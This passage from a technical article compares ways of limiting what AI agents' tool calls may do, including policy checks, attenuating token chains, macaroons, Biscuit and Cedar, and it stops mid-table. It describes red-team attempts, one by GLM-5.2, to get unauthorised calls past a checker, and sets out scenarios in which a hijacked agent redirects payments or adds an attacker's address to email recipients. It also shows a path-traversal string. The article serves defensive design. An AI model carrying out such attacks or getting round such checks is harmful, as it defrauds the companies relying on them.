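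ScopeGate makes its decision without a language model. It refuses a call if the policy doesn't list the tool, or if an argument that the policy limits to certain values doesn't have one of them. An amount of money must be a finite number from 0 up to a ceiling. For tools with side effects, the policy can also require a reference that guards against duplicates. If the check crashes, ScopeGate refuses the call.

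Mellafe Zuvic wrote 48 calls to try to get past the policy, using changed capitals, invisible characters, look-alike letters, wrong types and odd amounts. ScopeGate refused all of them. He then had GLM-5.2 try 40 times to get past ScopeGate, and told the model why each call had been refused. The model produced 29 unauthorised calls, 9 malformed ones and 2 legitimate ones, and ScopeGate refused every unauthorised call.

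These scores are not very surprising, because a program that compares an account with a list containing one allowed account will refuse every other account unless it has a bug. The tests are therefore mainly a search for bugs. There is little evidence on false refusals. ScopeGate allowed all ten legitimate calls in the main control test, but a check that wrongly refused a quarter of legitimate calls would still allow all ten about 6% of the time.

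### Nine types of constraint

ScopeGate reads its policy from the operator's configuration. Niyikiza instead puts the rules in the token, so every enforcement point that receives it has the same ones. This works only if they all interpret the rules identically. His draft therefore defines nine core constraint types and requires independent implementations to reach the same answer for the same value:

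| Type | What the argument must be | Example rule | Passes | Fails |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `exact` | Equal to one value | "EUR" | "EUR" | "USD" |
| `range` | A number within the bounds | 1 to 500 | 240 | 501 |
| `one_of` | On the list | A-17, A-22 | "A-17" | "X-99" |
| `not_one_of` | Absent from the list | X-99 | "X-98" | "X-99" |
| `contains` | An array with every listed element | audit | ["audit", "press"] | ["sales"] |
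| `subset` | An array with only listed elements | audit, sales | ["sales"] | ["audit", "press"] |
| `wildcard` | Anything | none | any value | nothing |
| `all` | Valid under every nested constraint | `contains` audit, and `subset` of audit, sales | ["audit", "sales"] | ["audit", "press"] |
| `any` | Valid under at least one nested constraint | 1 to 500, or exactly 1200 | 1200 | 800 |

The two array rules, `contains` and `subset`, are easy to misread. Suppose a company wants its audit team copied on every report an agent emails. With `contains`, the audit team must be among the recipients, but the agent can add anyone else, including an attacker. With `subset`, every recipient must be on the allowed list, but the agent can leave out the audit team. Even an empty array passes `subset`, because it has no element outside the list. The company needs both rules, which it can combine with `all`.

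Constraints inside `all` and `any` can contain further constraints. An attacker could submit a token with thousands of nested layers to exhaust the enforcement point's memory, so every enforcement point must limit how deeply constraints can nest. Niyikiza recommends a limit of 32 layers.

The core types are simple, but they cannot express some ordinary business rules. Each constraint applies to a single argument, so to set a limit of 500 for supplier A-17 and 100 for supplier A-22, the issuer would need a separate token for each. None of the types limits the number of decimal places, so a range from 0 to 500 accepts 0.001 as well as 240. Rules for file paths and web addresses need additional types because the same file or site can be written as several different paths or addresses.

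### Evaluating a call

Once the enforcement point has verified the token's signature and expiry, it checks the call in this order:

1. The token must list the tool.
2. If the tool has any constraints, every argument in the call must have one.
3. Every argument that has a constraint must be in the call.
4. Every value must satisfy its constraint.
5. If the enforcement point meets a constraint type it does not recognise, it refuses the call.

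The invoice agent's grant permits A-17 or A-22 as payee, an amount above 0 and up to 500, and any memo. Applied to six calls, the check gives these results:

| Call | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `send_payment`: X-99, 180, "Invoice 1043" | Refused | Payee is not on the list |
| `send_payment`: A-17, 180, "Invoice 1043" | Passes | All three values satisfy their rules |
| The same payment to A-17, plus `bank_account` | Refused | `bank_account` has no constraint |
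| `send_payment`: A-17, 180, no memo | Refused | `memo` is missing |
| `send_payment`: A-17, -180, "Invoice 1043" | Refused | Amount is not above 0 |
| `delete_supplier`: A-17 | Refused | The token does not list this tool |

The payment of 180 to A-17 then goes on to the proof-of-possession check.

The call with `bank_account` shows why unnamed arguments are dangerous. Suppose the payment service lets callers supply new bank details for a supplier that has just changed banks. The person who wrote the grant may not have known about this option, or the service may have added it later. A hijacked model could request a payment of 180 to A-17 and put the thief's account number in `bank_account`. The payee and the amount would satisfy their constraints, but the thief would receive the money.

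Under Niyikiza's draft, the enforcement point refuses this call because the grant has no rule for `bank_account`. Niyikiza calls this *closed-world* checking, in which a tool's constraints define the complete set of arguments that a call must have. Mellafe Zuvic's published algorithm for ScopeGate has no equivalent step. It checks the arguments that have a list of permitted values and then checks any amount, so an argument the policy doesn't mention reaches the tool.

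A missing argument can bypass a constraint when the tool fills in a default. For example, `send_payment` might pay a supplier's entire balance if the caller gives no amount. A check limited to the supplied arguments would find no number above 500 and allow the call, even if the balance was 40,000. The enforcement point prevents this by refusing any call that omits a constrained argument.

These rules can be inconvenient. The core types cannot express an optional argument. The invoice agent, for example, has to include a memo in every payment, even an empty one, because the grant has a `wildcard` constraint on `memo`. Deleting that constraint would make the enforcement point refuse any call with a memo. When a service adds a new argument, agents also cannot use it until somebody issues tokens that name it.

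An empty set of constraints, as in the entry `"send_payment": {}`, allows `send_payment` with any arguments, including a payment to X-99. If a grant has a single constraint, on `memo`, calls under it may contain only a memo, so they cannot pay anyone. Deleting that constraint leaves an empty entry, which allows any payment. If `send_payment` is left out of the token, the enforcement point refuses every call to it. The code that creates tokens should therefore treat an empty entry for a sensitive tool as an error.

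An enforcement point may also receive a constraint type that its software does not support, perhaps because the issuer uses a newer extension. Skipping that constraint and checking only the others would remove a restriction the issuer intended. Refusing the call may interrupt legitimate work, but it exposes the incompatibility. The same applies to a misspelt type such as `one_off`.

This safeguard applies only to unknown constraint types. The draft tells enforcement points to ignore unknown fields at the top level of a token, so if a company added its own `daily_limit` field there, standard enforcement points would not apply it. Both bounds of a `range` are also optional, so if the issuer writes `maximum` instead of `max`, software that ignores unfamiliar fields will enforce no upper limit.

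### Negative amounts

Someone who wants to limit payments to 500 may well write only half of the rule:

```json
"amount": { "constraint_type": "range", "max": 500 }
```

This accepts -180, along with every other negative number, because they are all less than 500. The result depends on the payment service, which might reject the request, record a refund or take money from the supplier. The grant in the running example avoids the problem by setting `min` to 0. It also sets `min_inclusive` to false, because bounds are inclusive by default and the agent could otherwise make payments of zero.

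One of the draft's own examples lets an agent search an index with a `limit` of at most 100 results but sets no minimum. Some software treats a limit of -1 as "no limit", so with such a tool the constraint would permit the unlimited search it appears to prevent.

Mellafe Zuvic's tests uncovered a related bug in an early version of ScopeGate. Floating-point arithmetic uses a value called NaN ("not a number") for results with no numerical answer, such as 0 divided by 0. Every greater-than or less-than comparison with NaN is false, so a program that refuses a payment only if `amount > 500` will allow NaN. ScopeGate now requires a finite number that satisfies `0 <= amount <= ceiling`, and NaN fails that test. The JSON standard doesn't allow NaN, but some parsers accept it, including the one in Python's standard library.

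The general lesson is to write the condition for permitting a call and refuse everything else. The same principle applies to lists.

### Lists of allowed and forbidden values

After discovering the fraud, the company might forbid payments to X-99 with `not_one_of`, but the thief can then open another account, X-100. A list of forbidden values, or *deny list*, contains only the dangers that somebody has already thought of, and the number of possible accounts is practically unlimited. An *allow list*, which contains the permitted values instead, excludes X-100 even before the account exists. A deny list of sensitive files at Tymshare would have had the same weakness.

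Changing the spelling can also get a value past a deny list. A list that contains only "X-99" lets through "x-99", as well as "X-99" followed by a space. If the payment service ignores capitalization and spaces, the money still reaches the thief. Many of the 48 calls in Mellafe Zuvic's test used tricks like these, but they failed because his policy used an allow list, which rejects any value not on it. Changing the value's type can also defeat a deny list. The array `["X-99"]` is not equal to the text "X-99", so it passes `not_one_of`, and a service that accepts several payees at once would pay X-99.

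Allow lists need more upkeep than deny lists, because the agent can't pay a new supplier until somebody adds it to the list. However, a missing entry in an allow list is easier to notice and fix, because the unpaid supplier will complain. The company may not notice a missing entry in a deny list until the money is gone.

An allow list is impractical for open-ended arguments such as memos and search queries, because nobody can list every legitimate value. A deny list adds little protection for these arguments, since an attacker can rephrase the forbidden text. So the issuer will often have to choose between `wildcard` and a tool that does not take free text.

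### General policy languages

A company with more complicated rules could use a general policy language. Cedar, an open-source language developed at Amazon Web Services, is one example. A Cedar policy permits or forbids an action by a particular party on a particular resource, and it can include further conditions:

```
permit (
  principal == Agent::"invoice-agent",
  action == Action::"send_payment",
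  resource in Group::"approved-suppliers"
)
when {
  context.amount > 0 &&
  context.amount <= resource.payment_limit
};
```

Here the supplier is the resource, and each supplier's record has its own payment limit. The policy can therefore allow payments of up to 500 to A-17 and up to 100 to A-22, which a single token cannot do with the nine core types. When the company approves a new supplier, it adds the supplier to the group without changing the policy. Cedar allows a request only if at least one `permit` policy matches it and no `forbid` policy does.

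The drawback of this flexibility is that the enforcement point needs the current supplier records to evaluate a call against the Cedar policy, whereas a token with a `one_of` constraint contains its own list of suppliers. Two enforcement points with different copies of the records may reach different decisions on the same call. Anyone who can change the records can also change what the agent may do, without changing the policy or the token.

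A Cedar policy also has no effect on arguments it doesn't mention. The program that turns a tool call into a Cedar request must therefore reject unexpected arguments such as `bank_account`, for example by checking the request against a strict schema. If a policy refers to a missing value, Cedar skips that policy and evaluates the others. Skipping a `permit` can only lead to a refusal, but skipping a `forbid` may let a call through. Cedar can check policies against a schema in advance, which catches most mistakes of this kind.

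The other drawback is that it is harder to analyze a policy, meaning to prove facts about it before anyone uses it. A program can tell that a limit of 300 is stricter than a limit of 500 by comparing two numbers, but comparing two Cedar policies takes an automated theorem prover, which has to consider every combination of supplier, amount and group membership. Cedar's designers left out loops and similar features partly to make such proofs possible. In a language without those restrictions, there may be no procedure that always finds the answer.

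Niyikiza names Cedar as a possible basis for additional constraint types but does not recommend a particular language. He points out that a language must let an enforcement point check whether a derived token's policy is at least as strict as its parent's, as well as decide whether a single call is allowed. He requires documentation of how much computation any additional type needs, and advises a time limit on any check whose running time could grow faster than the length of the argument.

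### Limits on requests in the AAP draft

*Agent Authorization Profile (AAP) for OAuth 2.0* (Cruz, 2026), an Internet-Draft, defines tokens that list an agent's permitted actions, each with constraints. Many of the standard constraints apply to the web request as a whole. They cover how many requests an agent may make, which domains and network addresses it may contact, when it may act, how large requests and responses may be, and how confidential the data may be. In one example, an agent may search the web only at `example.org` and make at most 50 requests an hour.

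The profile has no standard constraint for a payee or an amount. A deployment can define its own constraints, and one example restricts a publishing tool to `draft_only`. Every server that checks the token then needs code for each custom constraint. The validation rules in Cruz's first version require servers to enforce all constraints but do not specifically cover constraint names that a server doesn't recognise.

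AAP's main advantage over the nine core types is that it can limit the number of calls. Niyikiza's constraints apply to one call at a time, so they cannot limit how many payments the invoice agent makes. Under AAP, the issuer could allow three a day. To apply that limit, the server has to keep a record of earlier calls, and a service running on several machines needs a shared counter.

The hourly quota resets at the start of each clock hour, so an agent limited to 50 requests an hour can make 50 at 10:59 and another 50 at 11:00. A separate per-minute limit would prevent such bursts. Quotas apply to each token, so an agent with a new token starts again from zero.

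AAP has both allow lists and deny lists for domains. A deny list is useful here because allowing `example.org` also allows all of its subdomains, and an issuer may want to exclude one where anybody can upload files. The server checks the deny list first and refuses any domain that matches it, even if the domain is also on the allow list.

Cruz's second version and Niyikiza's draft both treat an action with an empty set of constraints as unrestricted. Cruz's version is ambiguous when a token lists the same action more than once. Suppose a token lists web search first for `example.org` and then for `trusted.example`. Cruz's draft allows a request if any entry grants it, but also requires the server to use the first entry that matches the action. A search at `trusted.example` would pass under the first rule but fail under the second. Niyikiza avoids this ambiguity by requiring enforcement points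 to reject an entry that lists the same tool twice.

AAP tokens also include the purpose of a task, such as "research_and_draft_article", and the server must refuse requests that clearly fall outside it. This could cover cases that nobody anticipated when listing values. But the draft gives no procedure for deciding whether a request fits a purpose, so one server may accept a call that another refuses. A server that used a language model to decide would again be open to prompt injection. The draft expired in August 2026 without a further revision.

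## Passing narrower authority from one agent to another

An orchestrating agent often leaves tool calls to other agents. Suppose it reads the invoice from A-17, decides that the company owes 180 and asks a payment agent to pay. The quickest way to authorise the payment agent would be to give it a copy of the root token and the private key needed to use it. The payment agent, or anyone who hijacked it, could then pay either supplier up to 500 at a time until the token expired, although the step needs only one payment of 180 to A-17.

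When Niyikiza announced his draft on the OAuth mailing list, he said that agents in multi-agent systems normally pass session-wide authority unchanged to every sub-agent. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) describes a related failure, the "transitive delegation problem". An orchestrator condenses the user's request into a subtask, and the sub-agent carries it out with a credential that identifies the program but not the user. The tool can authenticate the call but can't connect it to anything the user approved. A sub-agent that only has to summarise some documents may also inherit permission to change them.

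### Making a derived token

In Niyikiza's scheme, the payment agent generates its own key pair and sends the public key to the orchestrator. The orchestrator then writes a derived token. Here the root token runs from 09:50 to 10:50, and the orchestrator makes this token at 10:05 (with the long strings shortened):

```json
{
  "jti": "pay-0042",
  "iss": "urn:ietf:params:oauth:jwk-thumbprint:sha-256:KAKn...",
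  "iat": 1791367500,
  "exp": 1791367800,
  "del_depth": 1,
  "del_max_depth": 1,
  "par_hash": "q83f...",
  "cnf": { "jwk": { "kty": "OKP", "crv": "Ed25519", "x": "rAl9..." } },
  "authorization_details": [{
    "type": "attenuating_agent_token",
    "tools": {
      "send_payment": {
        "payee":  { "constraint_type": "exact", "value": "A-17" },
        "amount": { "constraint_type": "exact", "value": 180 },
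        "memo":   { "constraint_type": "wildcard" }
      }
    }
  }]
}
```

The `cnf` field contains the payment agent's public key, and `iss` identifies the orchestrator's key. The token lasts five minutes. `del_depth` gives the token's position in the chain, counting the root token as 0, and `par_hash` is a digest of the root token. The orchestrator signs the token with its private key and sends it to the payment agent with a copy of the root token. The orchestrator does not contact the issuer, so the issuer has no record of the derived token.

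To pay the invoice, the payment agent sends the enforcement point both tokens, the call and a proof signed with its own key. The agent can pay only 180 and only to A-17, but it could still make that payment more than once within the five minutes.

Niyikiza allows a derived token to have the same authority as its parent, which is useful when an agent moves its work to another process with a different key.

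### Six conditions for a valid child

For any token T, let C(T) be the set of calls that T permits, where a call is a function together with its arguments. The main safety property is:

```
C(child) ⊆ C(parent)
```

The parent token must permit every call that the child token permits. The payment agent's token meets this condition because the root token also permits a payment of 180 to A-17 with any memo. Since the number of possible memos is unlimited, an enforcement point can't check the condition by listing every call, so it checks six *invariants*, which are conditions that must hold for every token in the chain.

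**Delegation authority.** Only the parent's holder may make a child.

```
derived.iss == jwk_thumbprint_uri(parent.cnf.jwk)
```

The function on the right hashes a public key to produce a standard identifier. The enforcement point also verifies the child's signature with the parent's key. Without this invariant, a thief with a copy of the root token could create a child token naming the thief's own key, sign it with that key and then produce valid proofs, so proof of possession would no longer prevent the misuse of copied tokens.

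**Depth.** Each derivation adds one to the depth, up to a limit that holders can lower but not raise.

```
derived.del_max_depth <= parent.del_max_depth
derived.del_depth == parent.del_depth + 1
derived.del_depth <= min(MAX_DELEGATION_DEPTH,
                         parent.del_max_depth,
                         derived.del_max_depth)
```

`MAX_DELEGATION_DEPTH` is the enforcement point's own limit on delegation depth. The payment agent's token has a depth of 1 and a maximum of 1, so the agent cannot derive another token from it. Without an enforced limit, the agent could pass its authority to agents that the issuer never intended to include, or an attacker could overload the enforcement point with an enormous chain of tokens. The limit does not stop the payment agent from making calls on another agent's behalf. Niyikiza also warns against setting the limit too low, since agents that cannot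 derive narrower tokens may share broad ones.

**Lifetime.** A child cannot outlast its parent.

```
derived.exp <= parent.exp
now < derived.exp
parent.iat <= derived.iat < derived.exp
derived.iat - now <= MAX_IAT_SKEW
derived.exp - derived.iat <= MAX_TOKEN_LIFETIME
```

The first line is the main rule. Without it, an attacker with the orchestrator's key could derive a token at 10:49 that lasted until next month, despite the root token's one-hour limit. The other lines reject expired tokens and implausible dates. The draft recommends allowing 30 seconds for differences between clocks.

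**Capability.** The child may list only the parent's tools, with constraints at least as strict.

```
tools(derived) ⊆ tools(parent)
for every tool in derived:
    constraints(derived, tool) ⊑ constraints(parent, tool)
```

The symbol ⊑ means "at least as restrictive as". If the enforcement point skipped this comparison, an attacker who controlled the orchestrator could derive a token with a valid signature, depth and dates that allowed a payment of 50,000 to X-99.

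**Link to the parent.** The child contains a hash of one particular parent token.

```
derived.par_hash == base64url(SHA-256(parent signing input))
```

The signing input is the parent's encoded header and payload. Without the hash, an attacker could attach a child to a different token held by the same agent.

**Proof of possession.** The agent making the call must sign it with the key named in the last token of the chain, the *leaf*.

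```
pop_signature verifies under leaf.cnf.jwk
```

If this invariant were missing, anyone who copied the chain could use it.

### Derived tokens that fail

The orchestrator's software will sign whatever token it produces, including one that is too broad. A valid signature does not make the token acceptable, because the enforcement point compares the grants itself. The following changes to the payment agent's token would all make the chain invalid:

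| Change | Why the enforcement point rejects it |
|---|---|
| `amount` is exactly 600 | The root token stops at 500 |
| `payee` may be A-17 or X-99 | X-99 is not on the root token's list |
| `memo` is left out | The root token requires that argument |
| `bank_account` is added | The root token does not allow that argument |
| `delete_supplier` is added | The root token does not list that tool |
| `amount` is a range from 0 to 300 | The range includes 0, which the root token excludes |

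Leaving out `memo` would make the child token unusable, because a grant's constraints define exactly which arguments a call must have. The child would permit only calls without a memo, while the root token permits only calls with one. To limit the memo to one specific text, the orchestrator should keep the argument and replace `wildcard` with `exact`.

To make the range from 0 to 300 valid, the child has to repeat the root token's `min_inclusive` setting or use a higher minimum.

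The rule about arguments is different if the parent's entry is `"send_payment": {}`, which permits any payment. The child's maker can then add constraints on any of the arguments. If the parent's entry has constraints, an empty entry in the child is invalid because it would remove them all.

### Rules for comparing constraints

The draft gives a comparison rule for each of the nine core constraint types. Any type is acceptable under a parent's `wildcard`. Otherwise these rules apply:

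| Child's constraint | Valid when the parent has |
|---|---|
| `exact` | The same `exact` value, a `range` that includes it or a `one_of` list that contains it |
| `range` | A `range` with the same bounds or wider ones |
| `one_of` | A `one_of` list that contains all the child's values |
| `not_one_of` | A `not_one_of` list whose exclusions the child keeps |
| `contains` | A `contains` list whose required elements the child keeps |
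| `subset` | A `subset` list that contains all the child's allowed elements |
| `all` | An `all` whose every rule has a separate match in the child, at least as strict |
| `any` | An `any` in which each of the child's rules fits under some rule of the parent |
| `wildcard` | Only `wildcard` |

Removing a supplier from `one_of` or adding one to `not_one_of` narrows authority. Removing one from `not_one_of` widens it, because the agent may then pay a supplier that the parent excluded.

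The enforcement point must reject every combination that the draft does not explicitly allow. Only 19 of the 81 pairs of parent and child types can be valid. This rules out some safe combinations. For example, a child that allows amounts of 100 or 180 through `one_of` is narrower than a range up to 500, but the draft has no rule for `one_of` under `range`. The orchestrator would have to derive two tokens with exact amounts instead.

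Anyone who adds a constraint type has to supply a comparison procedure that is decidable, sound and deterministic. A decidable procedure always finishes. An attacker can write the child's constraints, and could otherwise choose ones that kept the enforcement point busy forever. The draft also rules out procedures that would finish but take impractically long in general.

A procedure is *sound* if it approves a child only when every value the child accepts would also satisfy the parent:

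```
if subsumes(parent, child) is true, then
for every value v: child.check(v) implies parent.check(v)
```

Suppose a parent permits files under `/data/public`, and the procedure only checks whether the child's path begins with that text. It would approve `/data/public/../private` and give the child access that its parent lacks, because `..` means "go up one folder" and the path leads to `/data/private`. The draft's sample rule for file paths resolves the `..` before comparing. A sound procedure must not approve an unsafe child, but it may reject some safe ones, as the core rules do with `one_of` under `range`.

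*Deterministic* here means that independent implementations always agree on whether to accept a token. If the enforcement point in Frankfurt rejected a token and the one in Dublin accepted it, an attacker would send the token to Dublin.

The draft's wording may cause disagreements of this kind. It defines "subsumes" to mean that the child is at least as strict as the parent, whereas in logic the broader statement usually subsumes the narrower one. Yet its explanation of `any` uses the word in the usual sense. The accompanying formula settles the meaning, but a programmer who relied on the prose could write the comparison backwards.

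Comparing two `all` constraints is the most complicated case. Suppose the parent requires an amount to be at most 1,000 and at most 500, and the child requires at most 400 and at most 800. A program might first match the parent's 1,000 with the child's 400, but that leaves 800 to match with 500, which fails. The draft's algorithm then goes back, tries other combinations, and finds that 1,000 matches with 800 and 500 with 400.

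Such a search can be very slow. With twelve rules on each side, if eleven of the parent's rules accept any match and the last accepts none, the algorithm could try 479,001,600 arrangements before failing. An attacker in the middle of a chain could construct this case. The draft mentions a much faster matching algorithm, Hopcroft-Karp, but does not require it.

### Verifying the chain

The enforcement point must already have the issuer's public key, which the draft calls a *trust anchor*. When the payment agent requests the payment, the enforcement point works from the root token to the leaf:

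1. It refuses oversized tokens and chains, and any chain in which two tokens have the same identifier. The recommended limits are 64 KiB for a token and 256 KiB for a chain.
2. It verifies the root token's signature with the trust anchor. It then checks that the token has depth 0, no parent hash, valid dates, a holder's public key and exactly one grant.
3. It takes the orchestrator's public key from the root token and uses it to verify the signature on the payment agent's token.
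4. It compares the payment agent's token with the root token, checking the issuer, depth, dates, grant and parent hash. In a longer chain, it would repeat steps 3 and 4 for each further token.
5. It checks that the number of tokens is one more than the leaf's depth. Here there are two tokens and the leaf has depth 1.
6. It checks the call against the leaf's grant.
7. It verifies the proof with the payment agent's key.

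The enforcement point refuses the call if any check fails. It must verify the tokens in order because each one supplies the key for verifying the next, and an attacker could have planted the key in an unverified token. It must also verify each token's signature before reading most of its contents, so that a stranger cannot crash the software with malformed data.

Comparing each token with the one before it is enough to limit the whole chain. If C(token 2) ⊆ C(token 1) and C(token 3) ⊆ C(token 2), then C(token 3) ⊆ C(token 1), and the same argument works for a chain of any length. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (2026) proves this by induction for *skills*, which are packaged abilities that can call one another, such as a research skill that uses a web-search skill.

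A chain of tokens can be too large to send in a request's headers, where credentials usually go. Niyikiza estimates that one token takes up 1 to 4 KB, and many web servers accept only 4 to 8 KB of headers, so he recommends sending the chain in the request's body.

### One child, two possible parents

The parent hash matters when an agent has several similar grants. Suppose the orchestrator holds token A for paying October's invoices and token B for organising a trade fair. Both name the same key, permit payments of up to 500 to A-17 and expire at 10:50. The orchestrator derives the payment agent's token, C, from A.

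The payment agent should present the chain (A, C). Without the hash, the agent could present (B, C) instead. C's signature would verify, because B also names the key the orchestrator used to sign C. The depth, dates and constraints would be valid too. Proof of possession would not reveal the switch, because the signed proof contains only C's identifier.

The substitution puts the payment under the wrong task, though it does not let the agent pay anyone else or send more money. The company's records would list an invoice payment as a trade-fair expense. If the company had cancelled the invoice task, or required a manager's approval for it, the enforcement point might check B's status instead of A's and allow the payment. The hash prevents the substitution because C contains A's digest, which differs from B's. Using a separate key for each task would also prevent it.

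### Macaroons, Biscuit and token exchange

Holders could narrow tokens without contacting the issuer long before AI agents needed to. Birgisson, Politz and colleagues (2014), in *Macaroons*, proposed a token for cloud services that its holder restricts by adding *caveats*, conditions that must be true when somebody uses it. The construction relies on HMAC, the hash computed with a secret key. If the bank creates a macaroon with the secret key K, two caveats give this sequence:

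```
s0 = HMAC(K,  identifier)
s1 = HMAC(s0, "payee = A-17")
s2 = HMAC(s1, "amount = 180")
```

The finished macaroon contains the identifier, both caveats and s2. Its holder can use s2 to add a third caveat, but can't remove the limit on the amount, because that would require computing s1 from s2. The bank knows K, so it can recompute the sequence and compare the result with s2.

Neil Madden, who asked about replaying parent tokens, also asked why agents should not just use macaroons. He pointed out that adding a caveat removes the earlier HMAC value, so the recipient never has the broader token. In Niyikiza's scheme, the recipient gets a copy of the parent token and lacks only its key. If the orchestrator's key leaks to the payment agent, that agent can use the root token.

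In his reply to Neil, Niyikiza accepted that his tokens lack this protection and said he would add the comparison to the draft. He also explained that the parent stays valid on purpose, so that an orchestrator can delegate to several agents and still act itself. He did not use HMAC because he wants tokens to work across organisations. Anyone who can verify a macaroon knows K and can forge one. A company would have to share its secret with every outside service that checked its tokens, or have those services contact it about every call.

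Macaroons are bearer tokens by default, but Birgisson and colleagues describe a caveat that requires a message signed with a particular private key. In *Non-bearer macaroons*, Madden (2018) suggested adding a final caveat containing a hash of the request and a timestamp. A thief who intercepts the resulting macaroon can't use it for another request. The method does not protect the original macaroon if someone copies it from the holder's storage.

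Speed was a major reason for choosing HMAC. On the 2014 team's server, an HMAC took 2.8 microseconds, an RSA signature took 458 and generating an RSA key pair took 54,000. HMAC's speed advantage matters less for agents, because Ed25519 keys take far less time to generate than RSA keys and an agent usually waits much longer for its model than for a signature.

Biscuit is a newer token format that replaces the shared secret with public-key signatures, so a verifier needs only the creator's public key. A holder can narrow a token by adding a block of checks, but cannot remove earlier blocks without invalidating the signature. Biscuit's documentation describes it as a bearer token that anyone with a copy can narrow.

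Biscuit's checks use a logic language derived from Datalog, in which a program draws conclusions from facts and rules. Clever Cloud's *Biscuit, the foundation for your authorization systems* (2021) explains that macaroon caveats were hard to use because each developer had to invent a way to write and test them. A common language solves that problem, but every verifier needs software that can run it.

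In Macaroons and Biscuit, every added restriction stays in the token and a request must satisfy all of them. Adding a restriction can therefore never widen authority, so neither system needs rules for comparing a child with its parent. Niyikiza's enforcement point checks the call only against the leaf's grant and depends on comparison rules to keep that grant within the root's. The leaf gives the agent's exact authority in one place, and any recipient can tell before the first call whether the chain is valid. But an error in a comparison rule could let an agent exceed its parent's authority. An enforcement point could guard against this by checking each call against every token in the chain, although the draft does not require it.

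With OAuth's *token exchange* standard, RFC 8693, the orchestrator instead sends its token to the authorisation server and asks for one with less authority, and the server decides whether to issue it. This needs a network request for every delegation and fails if the server is unavailable. The new token can also record which agents passed the authority along, but that record is only informational and doesn't let an enforcement point verify each narrowing for itself.

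Some agent systems are centralized by design. In *SentinelAgent* (2026), agents cannot sign their own tokens. A delegation service signs them after checking that each new scope fits within the previous one. Another Internet-Draft, *Credential Delegation for AI Agents* (2026), combines token exchange with DPoP so that the tokens require proof of possession. It also adds immediate revocation.

| Design | Requires the holder's key | Holder can narrow it offline | How restrictions are checked |
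|---|---|---|---|
| Macaroons | Only with an extra caveat | Yes | The service tests every caveat against the request |
| Biscuit | No | Yes | The verifier runs the checks in every block |
| Token exchange | Only when combined with DPoP or similar | No | The authorisation server approves each reduction |
| Niyikiza's tokens | Yes | Yes | The enforcement point compares each child with its parent, then tests the call against the leaf |

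The central designs may be simpler for an agent that works within one company, because the company's server is usually available and can refuse new tokens immediately. Offline narrowing is more useful when agents delegate very often or work across organisations.

### Cancelling a token

Verification without a network connection makes it hard to cancel a token. Suppose the company discovers at 10:06 that an attacker controls the orchestrator and has its key. The payment agent's token expires at 10:10, but the root token lasts until 10:50. Unless the company stops them in some other way, the attacker can use the root token to make payments and derive new tokens for another 44 minutes, however soon the payment agent's token expires.

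Niyikiza recommends that a leaf token last only as long as one call should take, and that a root token last no longer than the whole task. Yet the draft's recommended maximum lifetime is 90 days, and a company that issued 90-day tokens would have little protection if someone stole a key. Replacing the issuer's key is one emergency measure, but it invalidates every root token signed with the old key, including those of agents that are working properly.

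The alternative is for enforcement points to keep a list of cancelled tokens. Each token's chain includes all its ancestors, so an enforcement point that found the root token on the list could refuse every token derived from it, even those the issuer didn't know about. Niyikiza leaves this to a possible companion document. *AgentCap* (2026) already checks for revocation at every link. Such lists have to reach every enforcement point, so a service that relies on them is no longer fully offline.

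Macaroons and Biscuit face the same trade-off. Biscuit's documentation says that revocation requires information stored outside the token. For macaroons, Birgisson and colleagues suggest a caveat that requires recent confirmation from a revocation service. The client fetches this confirmation and sends it with its request. The macaroon soon becomes unusable if the service stops confirming it.

Cancellation is not instant under central control either. *SentinelAgent* estimates that an agent may continue for one update interval before it learns that its authority has ended. With ten-second updates and five calls a second, the agent could make up to 50 more calls.

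### A compromised agent in the middle

The six invariants stop an agent from widening authority, but an agent can also do harm by narrowing it. Suppose the orchestrator delegates to a purchasing agent, which delegates to the payment agent. The purchasing agent may pay A-17 or A-22 up to 500, and should derive a token for 180 to A-17. An attacker who controls the purchasing agent could instead derive a token for exactly 500 to A-22 and tell the payment agent to use it. The token would be valid, and an honest payment agent would have no reason to reject it.

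Adding a required element can be even more useful to an attacker. Suppose a parent token uses the `contains` constraint to let an agent email reports only if the recipients include the audit team. A compromised agent could derive a child token that requires both the audit team and the attacker's address. This counts as narrowing because fewer recipient lists satisfy it, but the next agent could then send a report only if it also sent the attacker a copy. Adding a `subset` constraint to the parent would prevent this by limiting who may receive reports.

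Niyikiza acknowledges that an enforcement point has to trust every intermediate holder to narrow tokens sensibly. A depth limit reduces the number of agents that must be trusted, but does not help detect a dishonest one.

*SentinelAgent* tries to detect malicious delegations with a language classifier. The off-the-shelf version caught only 1.7% of them in government delegation text. Training on 190 examples raised that to 88.3% (±8.5 percentage points), though the data set is small.

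*Agent-ZTA* (2026) addresses how to respond once a compromise is detected. If an attacker controls the purchasing agent, the payment agent's token may still be valid even though the instructions behind it are suspect. *Agent-ZTA* links security alerts about one agent to the workflows that depend on it, so a system can restrict the other agents without waiting for ordinary revocation. This protection depends on a reliable alert, which the tokens do not provide.

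### How far the comparison rules have been verified

Niyikiza says the capability invariant is the new part of his design. The other five invariants rely mainly on established methods such as signatures, hashes and expiry dates. He warns that an enforcement point that gets the capability check wrong does nothing to contain a compromised agent, and he requires implementers to test every pair of constraint types.

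Niyikiza's June 2026 revision describes three kinds of verification. He checked the set-based constraints, such as `one_of`, with Alloy, a program that tries every case up to a chosen size. The search covered up to 8 constraints and 8 values and found no counterexample. It would miss an error that appears only with nine values, although mistakes in simple set rules usually show up in much smaller cases.

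The draft uses Z3 for numeric and structural constraints, which can check a whole range of numbers without trying each one, but it gives no Z3 results yet. The remaining method, property-based testing, runs many generated inputs through Tenuo's Rust implementation. This can find bugs in the code but cannot prove that there are none.

Nobody appears to have published a completed proof or an independent analysis by October 2026. Niyikiza has invited other implementers to publish their own.

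## Where the check runs and what it leaves to the tool

Niyikiza's draft defines what an enforcement point must check but leaves each deployment to choose where that point runs. AuthZEN, a standard completed in January 2026, defines the messages between the component that makes a decision and the one that enforces it, and also leaves the location open. Cerbos, which sells authorisation software, argues in *Authorizing MCP tool calls at the gateway or inside the proxy* that the location determines which attacks a check can stop.

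The check on the invoice agent's payments could run inside the agent's own process, at a gateway between the agent and its tools, or inside the payment service. Tenuo's implementation supports several arrangements. It can run as a library within another program, as a separate verification service, or as a *sidecar*, a small program that runs next to a service. If every check also demands a signed proof, the four attackers fare as follows:

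| Attacker | Check in the agent's process | Check at a gateway | Check in the payment service |
|---|---|---|---|
| Thief with a copied token | Calls the service directly and never meets the check | Needs a route past the gateway | Cannot sign a proof |
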